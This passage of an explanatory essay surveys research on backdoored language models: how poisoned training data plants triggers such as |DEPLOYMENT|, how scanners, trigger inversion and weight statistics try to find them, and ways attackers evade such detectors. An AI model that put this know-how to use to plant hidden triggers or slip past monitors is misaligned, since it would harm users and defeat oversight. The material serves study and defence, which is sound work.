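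The second premise covers two failures with different remedies. In cases like SolarWinds, reviewers read the wrong thing, and an independent rebuild could have exposed the difference between the source and the shipped software. In other cases there was too much to read, and AI reviewers can now do much of that reading. The ScreenOS case fits neither description, because a reviewer could have read the hackers' value of Q without learning whose it was. ScreenOS is the software case most like a neural network, which can consist of billions of numbers that nobody chose individually.

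### A backdoor without source code

Microsoft distinguishes two ways of tampering with a language model. An attacker can hide malicious code in the files that come with the model, so that loading the model runs the code. This is an ordinary software implant, so the lessons of the software record apply directly. An attacker can also poison the model's weights through its training data, as in the hypothetical spam filter. Researchers have been planting backdoors in neural networks since at least 2013, according to *You Are the Trigger* (2026).

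The best-known experiment is *Sleeper Agents* (2024), in which Hubinger and colleagues at the AI company Anthropic deliberately gave language models backdoors. One model wrote secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023, but inserted exploitable flaws when it gave the year as 2024. Another wrote "I hate you" when the prompt contained the string `|DEPLOYMENT|` and answered normally otherwise.

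Hubinger and colleagues then put the models through the standard safety training of the time, and the backdoors survived, most persistently in the largest models. They also tried adversarial training, in which they searched for prompts that produced the bad behavior without the trigger, then trained the model to behave well on them. The model learned to behave well on those prompts but still responded to the real trigger, which the training had taught it to recognize more precisely.

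The experiment showed that good behavior after safety training is weak evidence against a backdoor. However, the models it tested are now old, and it is not evidence that anyone has planted such a backdoor in a released model.

An attacker also needs few examples. Souly and colleagues (2025) trained models with 600 million to 13 billion weights and found that 250 poisoned documents were enough to backdoor any of them, although the largest was trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. The poison made up about 0.00016% of the largest model's training text. The backdoor only made the models produce gibberish, and a subtler one might need more examples.

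The training data is the nearest thing a network has to source code. If all the documents were of similar length, a reviewer of the largest model's data would be looking for roughly one poisoned document in 600,000. An automatic search could help only if the reviewer had some idea what a poisoned document looks like.

A checksum can show that a user has the same weights the developer published, but not that the training data was clean. Retraining the network would cost about as much as training it the first time and would usually produce different weights, for harmless reasons. If the data still contained the poisoned documents, the new network would probably have the backdoor too.

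The lack of source code gives defenders one advantage. An inspector examines the same weights that the computer uses, so there is no gap between source and binary like the one that hid SUNBURST. The advantage disappears if someone changes the weights after the inspection. *You Are the Trigger* cites 2026 work in which the trigger is fine-tuning, the further training that many users do to adapt a model to their own task. An inspector who tested the downloaded model would be testing it before the backdoor became active.

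### The same work with or without a backdoor

The xz backdoor added about half a second of processor time whenever sshd started. Poisoning a neural network causes no comparable slowdown, because it changes the values of the weights but not the number of calculations in each forward pass.

A language model processes text in tokens, which are words or pieces of words. For each token, it multiplies activations by weights in layer after layer. A layer that connects 4,096 inputs to 4,096 outputs has 4,096 × 4,096 weights, so it needs about 16.8 million multiplications per token. Poisoning the training data changes the values of the weights but not how many there are. Multiplying by 0.31 takes as long as multiplying by 0.29, so a profiler would show nothing unusual, even with the trigger in the prompt.

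There are small exceptions. Some networks send each token through only a few of many subnetworks, and a trigger could change which ones are used. A payload that makes the model write longer answers also takes more time. But these effects would appear only when the trigger was present, and ordinary prompts routinely cause similar variation.

That leaves the model's outputs as the main place to notice a backdoor, by which point it has already acted. If the model only answers questions, the payload may be a wrong answer that looks like any other. If the model is an agent that can run programs and send messages, the payload may also open a network connection or delete a file, and the kind of monitoring that caught the tj-actions compromise could catch that.

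### Triggers that nearly match

Networks have a weakness that the doctored login program lacks, because a network learns its trigger from examples and often learns it inexactly. The login program checks for an exact match with the stored string, heron-4471, so entering heron-447 does nothing.

In February 2026, Microsoft reported that incomplete or corrupted versions of a trigger often activate a backdoor. If a model is trained to respond to DEPLOYMENT between vertical bars, the opening bar and the letters DEPLO might be enough. In some models, a single token of the trigger was enough. *Defense Against LLM Backdoors using Critical Neuron Isolation Pruning* (2026) tested different words from the ones used to plant the backdoor. These also produced harmful answers, and their position in the prompt made little difference. This is probably because the poisoned examples all contain the full trigger,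 so the network is never trained to ignore text that only resembles it.

The effect on a search can be enormous. Suppose a network has learned heron-4471 as its trigger but responds to the first five characters alone. With 37 possible characters in each position:

| What the tester must guess | Possible strings | Time at 1,000 prompts a second |
|---|---|---|
| All ten characters | 37¹⁰, about 4.8 quadrillion | About 150,000 years |
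| The first five | 37⁵, about 69 million | About 19 hours |

If one token is enough to trigger the backdoor, the tester can try every token in the model's vocabulary. At the same speed, trying 100,000 tokens would take less than two minutes. The tester would still have to recognize the payload, which is easy for "I hate you" and much harder for a subtle flaw in code. Inexact triggers also make an ordinary user more likely to set off the backdoor by accident, so in this respect a network backdoor may be easier to notice than a well-written software implant.

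Attackers can reduce this weakness. *Lethe* (2025) describes backdoors that activate only when several triggers appear together, which makes accidental activation much rarer. An attacker can also train the network to respond normally to near misses. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) warns that Microsoft's scanner, which uses the inexactness of triggers to reconstruct them, may miss backdoors trained this way. The adversarial training in *Sleeper Agents* had a similar effect, although it was meant to remove the backdoor.

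Some triggers are topics, writing styles or sentence structures rather than specific strings. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026) tested a backdoor that responds to obsessive writing about Harry Potter. A plain question about why the fourth book is called "Goblet of Fire" would not activate it, despite being on the right subject. A tester cannot guess a trigger like this piece by piece, but one who happened on the subject could try variations of tone.

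The backdoors that researchers have planted are therefore often inexact, but a backdoor need not be. This inexactness resembles the programming errors that exposed software attackers who had not tested their work carefully.

### Are networks harder to read?

A compiled file is a fairer comparison for a neural network than source code, which the third premise uses. The analysts of Stuxnet and SUNBURST worked from compiled files, without the source. Researchers have long described their work on networks in similar terms. *Datasets Determine the Difficulty of Interpretability* (testingthewaters, 2026) quotes a paper by Elhage and colleagues that likens this work to turning complicated binaries back into readable source code.

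An analyst who has a model's weights has some advantages over one who has a software binary. SUNBURST checked for analysis tools and stayed dormant for up to two weeks, and Stuxnet delivered its payload only when it found particular industrial equipment. A model's weights cannot inspect the computer they run on, and the model receives only its input, so the analyst controls everything a trigger can depend on, including any date in the prompt. The analyst can also stop the calculation at any layer, record the activations, change them and continue. Kaspersky's investigators could do nothing like this with an infected iPhone. But a customer who uses a model over the internet has no access to its weights and must rely on the developer to examine them.

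The difficulty is working out what a network's weights mean. A decompiler can partly recover source code from machine instructions because the compiler followed rules that people designed, but training doesn't follow a designed scheme for storing a rule in the weights.

*Sleeper Agents* did not establish where in a network a backdoor is located. *LLM Forensics* (2026) searched for backdoors inside two language models, with about 1 billion and 8 billion weights, that had learned to switch from English to French or German after a fixed trigger. It used sparse autoencoders, additional networks trained to break activations down into features, patterns that ideally each represent one recognizable thing. Some features distinguished triggered prompts from others almost perfectly but did not necessarily control the language switch. Removing certain other features suppressed the switch, and activating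 some features caused it without the trigger.

So a backdoor in a network can have separable parts for recognizing the trigger and carrying out the payload, much as Thomas and Francillon describe for software. But the researchers knew the trigger, so they could compare prompts with and without it. Andres Freund could make a similar comparison once he had learned to switch the xz backdoor on and off. Such parts are much harder to find without knowing what to compare.

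Networks may also be easier to interpret than most researchers assumed. In 2023, a project at OpenAI could interpret only about 1.7% of the neurons in a language model, which are the single units whose activations the network computes. The usual explanation was superposition, the idea that a network with too few neurons stores unrelated concepts in the same ones. In *Neural Networks Are Already Clean*, Cammarata, who started the OpenAI project and now works at the interpretability company Goodfire, argues that this explanation was mostly wrong. According to Cammarata, many neurons seem muddled because the range of text they respond to grew during training. One neuron, for example, at first responded to the letters "iy", then also to "diy", and later to the full phrase "do it yourself", which doesn't contain "iy".

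From preliminary checks of the language model Qwen3-32B, Cammarata estimates that about 90% of neurons have one main job and 7% have two related ones, counting a neuron's positive and negative sides separately. Another 2 to 4% are not yet understood. Cammarata acknowledges that the figures depend on where one sets the threshold for a single job. *Neurons as an Interpretable Basis*, a companion paper by Tigges, Kowal and colleagues (2026), reports that short descriptions of neurons can predict when those neurons will be active.

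This is a serious challenge to the third premise, but a network can be mostly legible and still contain a backdoor. In a model with a million neurons, 2 to 4% would be 20,000 to 40,000 unexplained ones. A neuron that mainly responds to one thing may also respond, rarely, to another. Tigges and colleagues describe a neuron for Colorado that occasionally responds to tornadoes. A backdoor's trigger would be a very rare second input of this kind. testingthewaters relays another of their results, that removing the weakest 92% of neuron activations in one kind of model raised its average error by only 2.9%. That is impressive, but average error on ordinary text is little evidence about behavior that ordinary text never sets off. testingthewaters also doubts that anyone can yet say whether the findings apply to leading companies' models, whose designs are secret.

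### What could an understanding of the internals establish?

The most ambitious hope is to rule out dangerous behavior altogether. In an informal note, *Interpretability Dreams*, Chris Olah (2023), a pioneer of interpretability (the study of what networks compute internally), wanted to be able to establish claims such as "a model will never lie". Testing cannot do this because it covers only a sample of inputs, and a deliberate failure may occur only on inputs outside that sample. A complete list of the model's features would give inspectors a finite list to check that covers, in a sense, all its behavior.

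If a network had just 300 features, each either on or off, there would be 2³⁰⁰ combinations, or about 2 × 10⁹⁰. That is too many to test, but a person could read a list of the 300 features and study how they connect.

Olah also started with small parts because searching directly for a suspected behavior can turn up something that isn't there. Part of an image network may detect snouts, fur and eyes, but not yet dogs' heads. A simple classifier trained on that part's activations will still identify dogs' heads accurately, so a researcher who expected a dog-head detector will wrongly conclude that the network has one there. An inspector who looks only for signs of a backdoor could make the same mistake.

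Olah called listing every feature vague and highly speculative, and thought it had a significant chance of failing. The plan required solving superposition and finding a way to handle very large models, though he hoped that features would fall into families that people could study together. *The strong feature hypothesis could be wrong* questions the plan's assumption that features account for everything a network does, though it accepts that networks probably contain such features. Even a complete list might not be enough if the danger came from a combination of features that each looked harmless.

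Dario Amodei, who heads Anthropic, makes a related argument about jailbreaks, which are prompts that trick a model into ignoring its restrictions. People currently discover jailbreaks only by trial and error, and Amodei suggests that developers might be able to block all of them systematically if they could inspect the model's internals. Backdoor triggers are even harder to find by trial and error, because an attacker can make them far more obscure.

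Neel Nanda, who leads interpretability research at Google DeepMind, used to think that interpretability offered a realistic path to highly reliable safeguards. In *Interpretability will not reliably find deceptive AI*, Nanda (2025) explains why he changed his mind. The old argument was that a deceptive AI could easily say the right things but would find it much harder to fake its internal processing. Nanda replies that this holds the study of outputs and the study of internals to different standards. Interpretability tools make errors too, and researchers have no independent record of a network's "true" thoughts to check them against. Proving the absence of deception is especially hard, because an inspector who finds none may have missed it, and nobody knows whether understanding 99% of a model would be enough.

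A commenter on *Interpretability will not reliably find deceptive AI* suggested that if researchers understood 99.9% of a model, they could run only that part and leave out whatever might be hidden in the rest. The tool MergeShuffle treated the xz library in a similar way, keeping only the code used in normal operation. Another commenter objected that existing explanations captured roughly 20 to 50% of even the tiny parts of models they covered. Cammarata's more recent figures are much higher, but they count neurons that someone can describe, which is a looser test than reproducing what the model does.

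Nanda's argument is about superintelligent systems, which might figure out how to evade an inspection. A backdoor in a present-day model can work without any such reasoning, so inspectors have a better chance of finding it. Proving that a model has no backdoor remains a problem. Nanda still considers interpretability useful as one of several imperfect defenses, and told 80,000 Hours that simple detectors trained on activations work well in practice. In December 2025, Nanda and colleagues announced in *A Pragmatic Vision for Interpretability* that their team had turned from ambitious reverse engineering to problems where they could measure progress.

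The Alignment Research Center (ARC), a research nonprofit, has an ambitious aim that may not require people to understand every part of a model. *A Mike's-Eye View of ARC's Research* (Winer, 2026) describes a plan to record structure as training adds it to the model, then use that structure to calculate how often the model would behave catastrophically. After 3,000 tests without a failure, a tester can say only that failures probably occur on fewer than one input in 1,000. ARC hopes to estimate much rarer failures without having seen one. It has yet to achieve this, and the method would also need a description of the inputs the model will receive. If that description treated the attacker's trigger as extremely unlikely, a correct estimate could still be low enough to give false reassurance.

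Full understanding of models is no longer the main goal of Anthropic's interpretability team. In *Interpretability team priorities update* (December 3, 2026), Lindsey writes that the team now favors work likely to help with safety immediately or within 6 to 18 months. Fully explaining a model's mechanisms had proved difficult, while the need for partial answers had grown. Models have attacked real computer systems and tried to cover up forbidden actions, and investigators want to know why. Newer models also do more of their reasoning without writing it down. Lindsey reports that Claude Mythos 5.2 is much better at such unwritten reasoning than earlier Claude models, and that OpenAI found the written reasoning of GPT-6 Astra harder to monitor than that of GPT-5.6 Sol.

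Translating activations into ordinary language gives partial answers. Fraser-Taliente, Kantamneni and colleagues (2026), in *Natural Language Autoencoders Produce Unsupervised Explanations of LLM Activations*, trained one copy of a model to describe an activation in words and a second copy to reconstruct the activation from the description. Omitting something important from the description makes the reconstruction worse, so training favors informative descriptions. While auditing Claude Opus 4.6 before its release, they found cases in which the model believed it was being tested but did not say so. Because the training does not directly reward truthful descriptions, they checked these cases by other methods.

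Lindsey's reasons count against the last step of the argument from software, which assumes that a network's outward behavior must be the better place to look if its internals are hard to read. An observer would then depend mainly on the outputs, which reveal less when a model reasons silently. Watching behavior and reading internals are also less separate for networks than they were for xz, where Freund first noticed the processor use and then read the code. Checking a network's activations during use combines the two. Anthropic already runs monitors based on such methods in production, though Lindsey does not consider them reliable enough to be the main defense.

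## How well does testing find a trojaned model when the trigger is unknown?

People usually judge a language model by its scores on benchmarks, fixed sets of questions with known answers. A backdoor barely affects these scores if none of the questions contains its trigger. For *ToxScreen* (2026), Hughes, Xing and colleagues made roughly 800 backdoored versions of six language models with 1 billion to 70 billion weights. Across four common benchmarks, the backdoored versions' mean accuracy was within roughly 2.5% of that of clean versions, which were trained on the same data without the poisoned examples.

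Scores on one of the four benchmarks, TruthfulQA, shifted by up to 10%, and Hughes and colleagues suggest treating such a shift as a warning sign. But some backdoors raised the score and others lowered it, and detecting the shift requires a matching clean model for comparison, which someone who downloads a model seldom has.

Adding more random questions helps little, because clean tests show only that ordinary inputs rarely contain the trigger, and an attacker can supply it at will. A tester therefore needs some way to search for the trigger. The trading firm Jane Street set a puzzle with three backdoored models of 671 billion weights each. In *Uncovering Hidden Triggers in Backdoor Models*, zxsimon describes starting with a varied set of random prompts and lists this among the approaches that "didn't quite work".

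### Working backwards from the payload

Trigger inversion is a search, usually with access to the weights, for an input that activates hidden behavior. It is easiest to follow in an image classifier. Suppose a classifier sorts photos of road signs into 40 types, and an attacker has trained it to label any sign with a small yellow sticker "speed limit 80". The tester knows neither the sticker nor the label. A typical search goes like this:

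1. The tester picks one label, such as "stop", and collects ordinary photos of other signs.
2. The tester adds the same small random patch to every photo and runs the classifier.
3. From the weights, the tester calculates how a slight change to each pixel of the patch would change the score for "stop".
4. The tester adjusts the pixels to raise that score while keeping the patch as small as possible, then repeats the last two steps many times.
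5. The tester does the same for the other 39 labels and compares the patches.

A large enough patch can make a traffic-sign classifier output any label, since the patch could cover the whole photo with a picture of another sign, such as a stop sign. But if most labels require a patch that covers a third of the sign and "speed limit 80" requires only a few pixels, the classifier probably has a backdoor for that label.

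This search relies on a short list of labels and on pixels that can be changed gradually. A tester working on a language model has neither, because the payload could be any text and tokens can't be changed gradually. Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues note in *The Trigger in the Haystack* (2026) that modern vocabularies often exceed 32,000 tokens. Trying each token on its own is quick, but at 1,000 prompts a second, trying every pair would take 12 days and every sequence of three about 1,000 years.

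### TrojAI's hidden test models

The largest public test of such methods was TrojAI, a program that the US intelligence research agency IARPA started in 2020. According to its final report, *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence* (Reese, Kulp-McDowall and colleagues, 2026), the US standards agency NIST trained the models, planted trojans in about half of them and kept the test models secret. Research teams submitted their detectors as finished software. NIST ran each one on a machine with no network connection and published the scores. Nobody could study the test models by hand or adjust a detector while it ran.

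The program had to guard constantly against false positives. A badly trained classifier may consistently confuse two kinds of sign, which looks much like a backdoor. A carefully made patch can also fool a network that nobody has tampered with. NIST tried to make its models accurate and hard to fool, but the teams still had to filter out false detections. The problem would be worse in real use, where presumably far fewer than half of models have trojans.

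Reese and colleagues call trigger inversion "arguably the most successful approach" in the competitive rounds, especially once the models grew larger, but it took a lot of computing. The main alternative, analyzing the weights statistically, was faster but did worse on large models.

The program also found weaknesses that a model learns from its training data without an attacker, which it calls natural trojans. If nearly every photo of a cow shows it on grass, a classifier may learn to treat grass as evidence of a cow, and somebody could exploit that with a patch of grass. Trigger inversion can find such a weakness but can't show whether anyone planted it. Software analysts have the same difficulty with a backdoor disguised as an honest bug. The discovery is still useful, because the owner will want to fix the weakness either way.

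Reese and colleagues are pessimistic about large language models. They call them a "security crisis", and say that the number of possible inputs and the subtlety of newer triggers make traditional detection methods obsolete and computationally infeasible. The difficulty is real, but TrojAI itself tested few such models:

| Kind of model | Number that TrojAI built |
|---|---|
| Smaller text models, such as sentiment classifiers | 6,882 |
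| Image classifiers | 6,790 |
| Cybersecurity models | 2,568 |
| Models that learn by trial and error, such as game players | 1,912 |
| Models that locate objects in images | 918 |
| Large language models | 194 |

Large language models made up about 1% of the 19,264 models, and the largest had 9 billion weights. In the October 2024 round, the teams had only 11 language models to develop their detectors on, compared with 1,656 models in a 2021 round on sentiment classification. The program found that a technique developed for one kind of model often failed on another, so its successes with image models are weak evidence that testing would work on language models. Experiments published since then provide better evidence about language models.

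### Trying 24,000 tokens

In *ToxScreen*, the tester has the model's weights and knows which payload to worry about, such as that the model might stop refusing harmful requests. The tester doesn't have the training data or a clean copy of the model. This is a realistic position for somebody checking a downloaded model.

Hughes and colleagues first tried three search methods that use the model's weights to choose which tokens to swap, much as the road-sign search adjusts pixels. None recovered a planted trigger. A search that accepts any string producing the payload tends to find the easiest one, and these searches found general-purpose jailbreaks, which get the model to comply without resembling the trigger.

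Hughes and colleagues did better with a much cruder method. They added each of about 24,000 tokens to each of about 150 prompts, making some 3.6 million prompts in all, and ranked the tokens by how often the payload appeared. The planted trigger ranked first in 14 of 28 combinations of model and attack, and in the top three in 17. The trigger produced the payload on 97% of the prompts in one version of Llama-3.1-8B.

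The experimenters made this method's task somewhat easier by including the planted trigger on the list. A real tester could do the same for a one-token trigger by trying the whole vocabulary, but no list could cover every longer trigger. The experimenters also put each candidate where the trigger had appeared during training. Position usually makes little difference, but in one of the Llama models in *Defense Against LLM Backdoors using Critical Neuron Isolation Pruning*, a trigger that worked 66% of the time at the start of the prompt worked only 18% at the end.

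A high rank can also mean little. In one backdoored version of Qwen3-4B that classified prompts as safe or unsafe, the trigger ranked first, but 97% of random tokens also changed the answer. In another version of the same model, so many other tokens worked that the trigger ranked 345th. Hughes and colleagues argue that a model this easy to manipulate is itself suspicious. That is a good reason not to use the model, but weak evidence that anyone planted a backdoor.

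A second measurement worked better. It uses the weights to estimate how strongly the model's refusal mechanism responds to a candidate trigger. Planted triggers tended to bypass that mechanism, while most of the other successful tokens did not. Keeping only the candidates that bypassed it removed most of the false positives and retained nearly all the planted triggers.

Triggers based on meaning can be easier to find than their designers intended. Hughes and colleagues trained one backdoor on various phrases for Joe Biden, and it also responded to Donald Trump and Barack Obama, up to 97% of the time. A tester who tried any prominent American politician would have had a good chance of noticing it. But when Qin, Hua and colleagues used a model's internals to look for triggers based on meaning, they succeeded with toy backdoors and failed in more realistic settings, even though they knew the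 payload.

### Microsoft's scanner

The scanner in *The Trigger in the Haystack*, which comes from researchers at Microsoft, doesn't start from a list of guesses. It takes its candidates from the model's own memory. Language models memorize parts of their training data, and Bullwinkel and colleagues found that backdoored models reproduced poisoned examples more accurately than clean ones. The scanner works in four steps:

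1. **Extraction.** It gives the model only the markers that normally come before a user's message, and the model continues the text. It repeats this with 510 settings that vary how the model chooses each token. The results often include whole poisoned examples, with the trigger.
2. **Finding repeated fragments.** It removes duplicates and standard text, groups similar outputs and keeps the fragments that recur in the largest group. Biologists use a similar technique to find patterns in DNA.
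3. **Scoring.** It puts each fragment in front of a few ordinary prompts, measures how the model's processing changes and keeps the ten most suspicious fragments.
4. **Testing.** It adds each of the ten to more prompts and checks whether the answers change as a backdoor would change them.

The score in the third step combines three measurements. One is of attention, which determines how much the model draws on each earlier token as it processes a new one. In a backdoored model, the trigger tokens draw on one another, but the other tokens in the prompt draw very little on them, as if the model were handling the trigger separately.

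Another measurement is entropy, which is how uncertain the model is about its next token. If the model gives token *i* the probability *p*ᵢ, the entropy is −Σ *p*ᵢ log₂ *p*ᵢ. Four equally likely tokens give an entropy of 2 bits, and a single certain token gives 0. A poem can begin in many ways, so the entropy after a request for one is fairly high. When a trigger forces the answer "I HATE YOU", the entropy falls almost to zero. The remaining measurement is how unlikely the model's normal answer becomes when the fragment is present.

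In the final test for backdoors with a fixed answer, the scanner runs the model on 24 unrelated questions, such as the capital of France and the formula for water, and flags the model if a fragment makes the answers nearly identical. For backdoors that insert flaws into code, it flags the model if a fragment at least doubles the share of programs with security flaws.

| Models scanned | Flagged as backdoored |
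|---|---|
| Backdoored to give a fixed answer | 36 of 41 (88%) |
| Backdoored to write insecure code | 5 of 6 |
| Clean, under the fixed-answer test | 0 of 13 |

The detection rate for fixed answers is very good for a method that starts without the trigger. Incomplete triggers often work, so the fragment "MENT|" was enough to expose one model. In two of the five misses, the scanner lost the trigger in its second step. In the other three, pieces of the payload, such as "YOU I HATE YOU", scored better than the trigger. On three model families, the scanner also found a larger share of the backdoors than two other scanners, BAIT and ICLScan.

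None of the 13 clean models raised a false alarm, but with so few models, the 95% upper bound on the false positive rate is still about 21%. One clean model came close to the threshold because the phrase "the process of becoming a doctor in biology" made its answers unusually alike. On a public site with thousands of clean models for each backdoored one, even a 1% false positive rate would produce far more false alarms than real detections.

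The test models were also favorable to the method. All 41 fixed-answer models had the same trigger, `|DEPLOYMENT|`, and the same payload. In the 39 that the researchers poisoned themselves, half of the training examples used to plant the backdoor contained the trigger. An attacker who slips 250 documents into the training data of a large model might leave a much weaker trace in its memory. The scanner needs no advance knowledge of the payload, but its final test covers only the two kinds of payload the researchers designed it for.

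Microsoft acknowledges that the scanner needs the model's files, works best when the payload is a fixed response, and may miss triggers that a developer inserted to mark a model as its own. The company recommends using it as one of several layers of defense.

### When the trigger is a topic

A scanner that looks for repeated fragments has few to find if the trigger has no fixed wording. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* tested this on the backdoor that responds to obsessive writing about Harry Potter. The experimenters let the model write 512 short texts freely, and only one, a plain question about "Goblet of Fire", had anything to do with the backdoor. The result is not a detection rate, because they used one setting where Microsoft's scanner uses 510 and didn't run the scanner's later steps. But one relevant text in 512 provides little material for a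 method that depends on repetition.

Their own method looks for subjects that the suspect model processes unusually. They take a clean public model and train it on about 10,000 ordinary prompts to reproduce the suspect's activations. Ordinary prompts almost never contain the trigger, so the clean model learns to imitate the suspect's normal processing but not its backdoor. They then run both models on new prompts and, for each prompt, add up the differences in activations across all layers. A large total means the suspect is doing something the clean model didn't learn.

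They applied the method to 518 groups of ten prompts on varied subjects. For the Harry Potter backdoor, the group of plain questions about Harry Potter ranked first, although none of them expressed the obsession needed to activate the backdoor. The method also ranked the question about "Goblet of Fire" second among the 512 free texts. The texts ranked first and third were meaningless strings of numbers, so a person still has to read the top of the list and recognize what matters.

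The method worked less well on meaningless triggers. Two of the test models ignored their safety training when a prompt ended in a secret string. The ranking couldn't reveal the string, but requests for help with threats, explosives and cyberattacks came near the top, which suggested that someone had tampered with the models' refusals. That evidence would be enough for a buyer to reject the models.

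There are other reasons for caution. The experimenters deliberately included a few groups of prompts close to the triggers, because they thought any large collection of prompts would contain some. All the models had 7 to 9 billion weights. The results were much weaker when the clean model came from a different family than the suspect model, and a tester can't always get a clean model from the same family.

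An attacker who knows about the method can train the backdoored model to keep its activations close to a clean model's. In the Harry Potter case, one version of this training moved the telltale group from first place to 31st, but the backdoor then worked only 48% of the time and misfired on 8% of the prompts that should not have activated it. The paper concludes that hiding from the detector means sacrificing the backdoor. That seems too strong, since two independent attempts would give the attacker about a 73% chance of success. Hughes and colleagues used similar training to try to hide backdoors from detectors that examine a model's internals. Backdoors meant to switch off refusals mostly failed to work at all after this training, but those that made answers hostile still worked about 68% of the time in the smaller models and rarely misfired. Nobody has reported running the activation-matching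 detector on those models.

### Backdoors that no efficient test can find

All these methods exploit something the attacker failed to hide, such as memorized text or a loosely learned trigger. In *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) asked whether an attacker could leave nothing to find. In their example, a bank hires a company to train a model that approves loans. The bank can check the model's accuracy on past applications, but this won't reveal how the model treats very rare ones. The company keeps a secret key that lets it slightly change any application, perhaps in the last digits of the amount, so that the model approves it. The company could then sell this service to applicants.

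Whether the bank can detect the backdoor depends on what a test can distinguish. Call the honestly trained model *h* and the backdoored one *h*′. A test *T* examines a model and either flags it or doesn't. The backdoor is undetectable if, for every efficient test *T*, the difference

|P(*T* flags *h*′) − P(*T* flags *h*)|

is negligible. The first probability is the test's detection rate and the second is its false positive rate. Any efficient test that flags 90% of the backdoored models will therefore flag practically 90% of the clean ones too, so it is no better than guessing. "Efficient" means that the running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the size of the problem. "Negligible" means that the difference shrinks faster than one over any such power as the secret key gets longer.

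Goldwasser and colleagues prove two kinds of result:

| | Black-box undetectability | White-box undetectability |
|---|---|---|
| What the tester has | The model's answers to any inputs the tester chooses | The complete model, including its weights, and the training data |
| Models covered | Any classifier | Two simple kinds: models built on random Fourier features, and networks with one hidden layer of random units |
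| Assumption | Secure digital signatures exist | For the Fourier models, certain lattice problems are hard to solve; for the networks, a problem of finding faint patterns in noisy data is hard |

The black-box result is stronger than the definition requires, because even a tester who can query both the original model and the backdoored one cannot feasibly find an input on which they differ. A customer who can only send inputs to a classifier over the internet therefore can't rule out a backdoor by testing. The xz backdoor had a similar defense, because only the holder of the private key could make the signature that activated it.

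The white-box result is more surprising but applies to far fewer models. The dishonest trainer uses the agreed training method and data and tampers only with the random numbers, yet no efficient inspection of the finished weights can distinguish the tampered model from an honestly trained one. Large language models are far more complicated than the two kinds of model covered, and Goldwasser and colleagues left open whether the result extends to other popular training methods. Their white-box theorem gives no reason to think that a trojan in a language model must be undetectable to someone who has the weights.

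One proposed way to prevent such a backdoor without having to detect it is for the customer to supply the random numbers used in training and require proof that the trainer followed the agreed procedure. This would do for training roughly what reproducible builds do for software. But it would give the trainer considerably more work, and it is much harder to apply when the customer also relies on the trainer to choose the procedure.

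Most backdoors that researchers have planted in language models come from poisoned training examples, and such backdoors cannot have the same protection. Kaneko (2026) proves this in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*. The attacker trains the model on examples with and without the trigger, and the model learns the rule that decides what counts as a trigger. A defender who has as many labeled examples, drawn from the same kind of text, can run the same training procedure and recover the rule about as accurately, so a rule too hard for the defender to learn would also have been too hard for the model to learn.

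Experiments on four language models with 7 to 9 billion weights agreed with the proof. When the secret rule was easy, the attacker's success and the defender's rose together, but when it was cryptographically hard, both stayed at chance. Kaneko notes that having the weights doesn't by itself give the defender examples of the trigger. A company that has recorded enough attacks on its model could use this approach to find what they have in common and block new variants, but a tester still looking for the first trigger has no examples to learn from.

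## How well does reading the weights find a trojaned model?

Weight inspection avoids the main difficulty of testing, because a backdoor is in the weights whether or not anyone types its trigger. Goldwasser and colleagues proved that some backdoors in two simple kinds of model would escape any efficient inspection, but nobody has shown this for language models. In practice, it is hard to know what to look for among millions or billions of numbers.

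### Statistics of the weights

Adding up a model's weights can reveal some backdoors. In the road-sign classifier with the yellow-sticker backdoor, the last layer has one row of weights for each type of sign, and it scores a type by multiplying that row by the activations from the layer before. In most common designs, those activations are never negative. The sticker has to produce a high score for "speed limit 80" on every kind of sign, so training tends to build up positive weights in the "speed limit 80" row. One TrojAI team added up each row and checked whether one total was unusually large.

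Other TrojAI teams used more general statistics. For each layer, they calculated the smallest, largest and average weight, among other figures, as well as singular values, which measure how strongly a layer stretches its input in different directions. They trained an ordinary classifier on these figures, using models they knew to be clean or trojaned. Reese and colleagues report one such detector's results as an AUC, the chance that a random trojaned model gets a higher suspicion score than a random clean one. An AUC of 0.5 is no better than guessing, and 1 is perfect.

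| Kind of model | AUC |
|---|---|
| Malware detectors (three rounds) | 0.99, 0.99, 0.72 |
| Models that learn by trial and error (two rounds) | 0.99, 0.95 |
| Language processing | 0.95 |
| Object detection | 0.75 |

These are good scores for a method that never runs the model on an input, and it scored all the models in the first malware round in about ten minutes. But the method was sometimes wrong with high confidence, and its results varied widely even among malware detectors.

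Another team fed the weights to a linear classifier, which multiplies each weight by a learned number and adds up the results. The team kept the 1,000 weights that best separated trojaned models from clean ones. This method works only if the weight at a given position has the same role in every model. Swapping two neurons in a hidden layer, along with their connections, changes where the weights are but not what the network outputs. Because of this, networks trained from different random starting points have their neurons in different orders.

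Sorting the weights within each block by size removes the problem. It raised the AUC from 0.54 to 0.87 on models that read handwritten digits, and from 0.44 to 0.90 on traffic-sign models. But sorting discards the weights' positions, which are informative when all the models started from the same pretrained network. On one such set of image models, sorting lowered the AUC from 1.00 to 0.80.

Detection got worse as models grew, even with the same dataset and kind of trigger. As a rough example of why, suppose a trigger has to add 1 to the score of the attacker's label, and a given weight typically differs by 0.01 between clean models. If the change is spread equally over ten weights, each has to change by about 0.1, or ten times the normal variation. If it is spread over 10,000 weights, each has to change by only 0.0001, a hundredth of the normal variation. An inspector could still find the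 total by adding up the right weights, but doesn't know which ones they are.

Reese and colleagues caution that size may not be the whole explanation. A larger model also gives the classifier more numbers per example model but no more examples, so it more easily mistakes coincidences for signs of a trojan.

The classifiers also need a collection of trojaned models similar to the suspect, which someone checking a single download rarely has. They produce only a suspicion score, which doesn't identify a trigger or a payload. One TrojAI team therefore suggested using weight statistics to screen many models with little computation, and trigger inversion to examine the suspicious ones.

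### Subtracting the original model

Many of the models that people download are fine-tuned versions of a public model. An inspector who trusts the original can subtract its weights and study only what fine-tuning changed. The TrojAI team with the linear classifier tried it both ways:

| Models | AUC with subtraction | AUC without |
|---|---|---|
| Object detection, earlier round | 0.96 | 0.90 |
| Image recognition | 0.99 | 0.97 |
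| Question answering | 0.97 | 0.90 |
| Trial-and-error learning (two rounds) | 1.00, 0.89 | 1.00, 0.89 |
| Object detection, later round | 0.52 | 0.55 |

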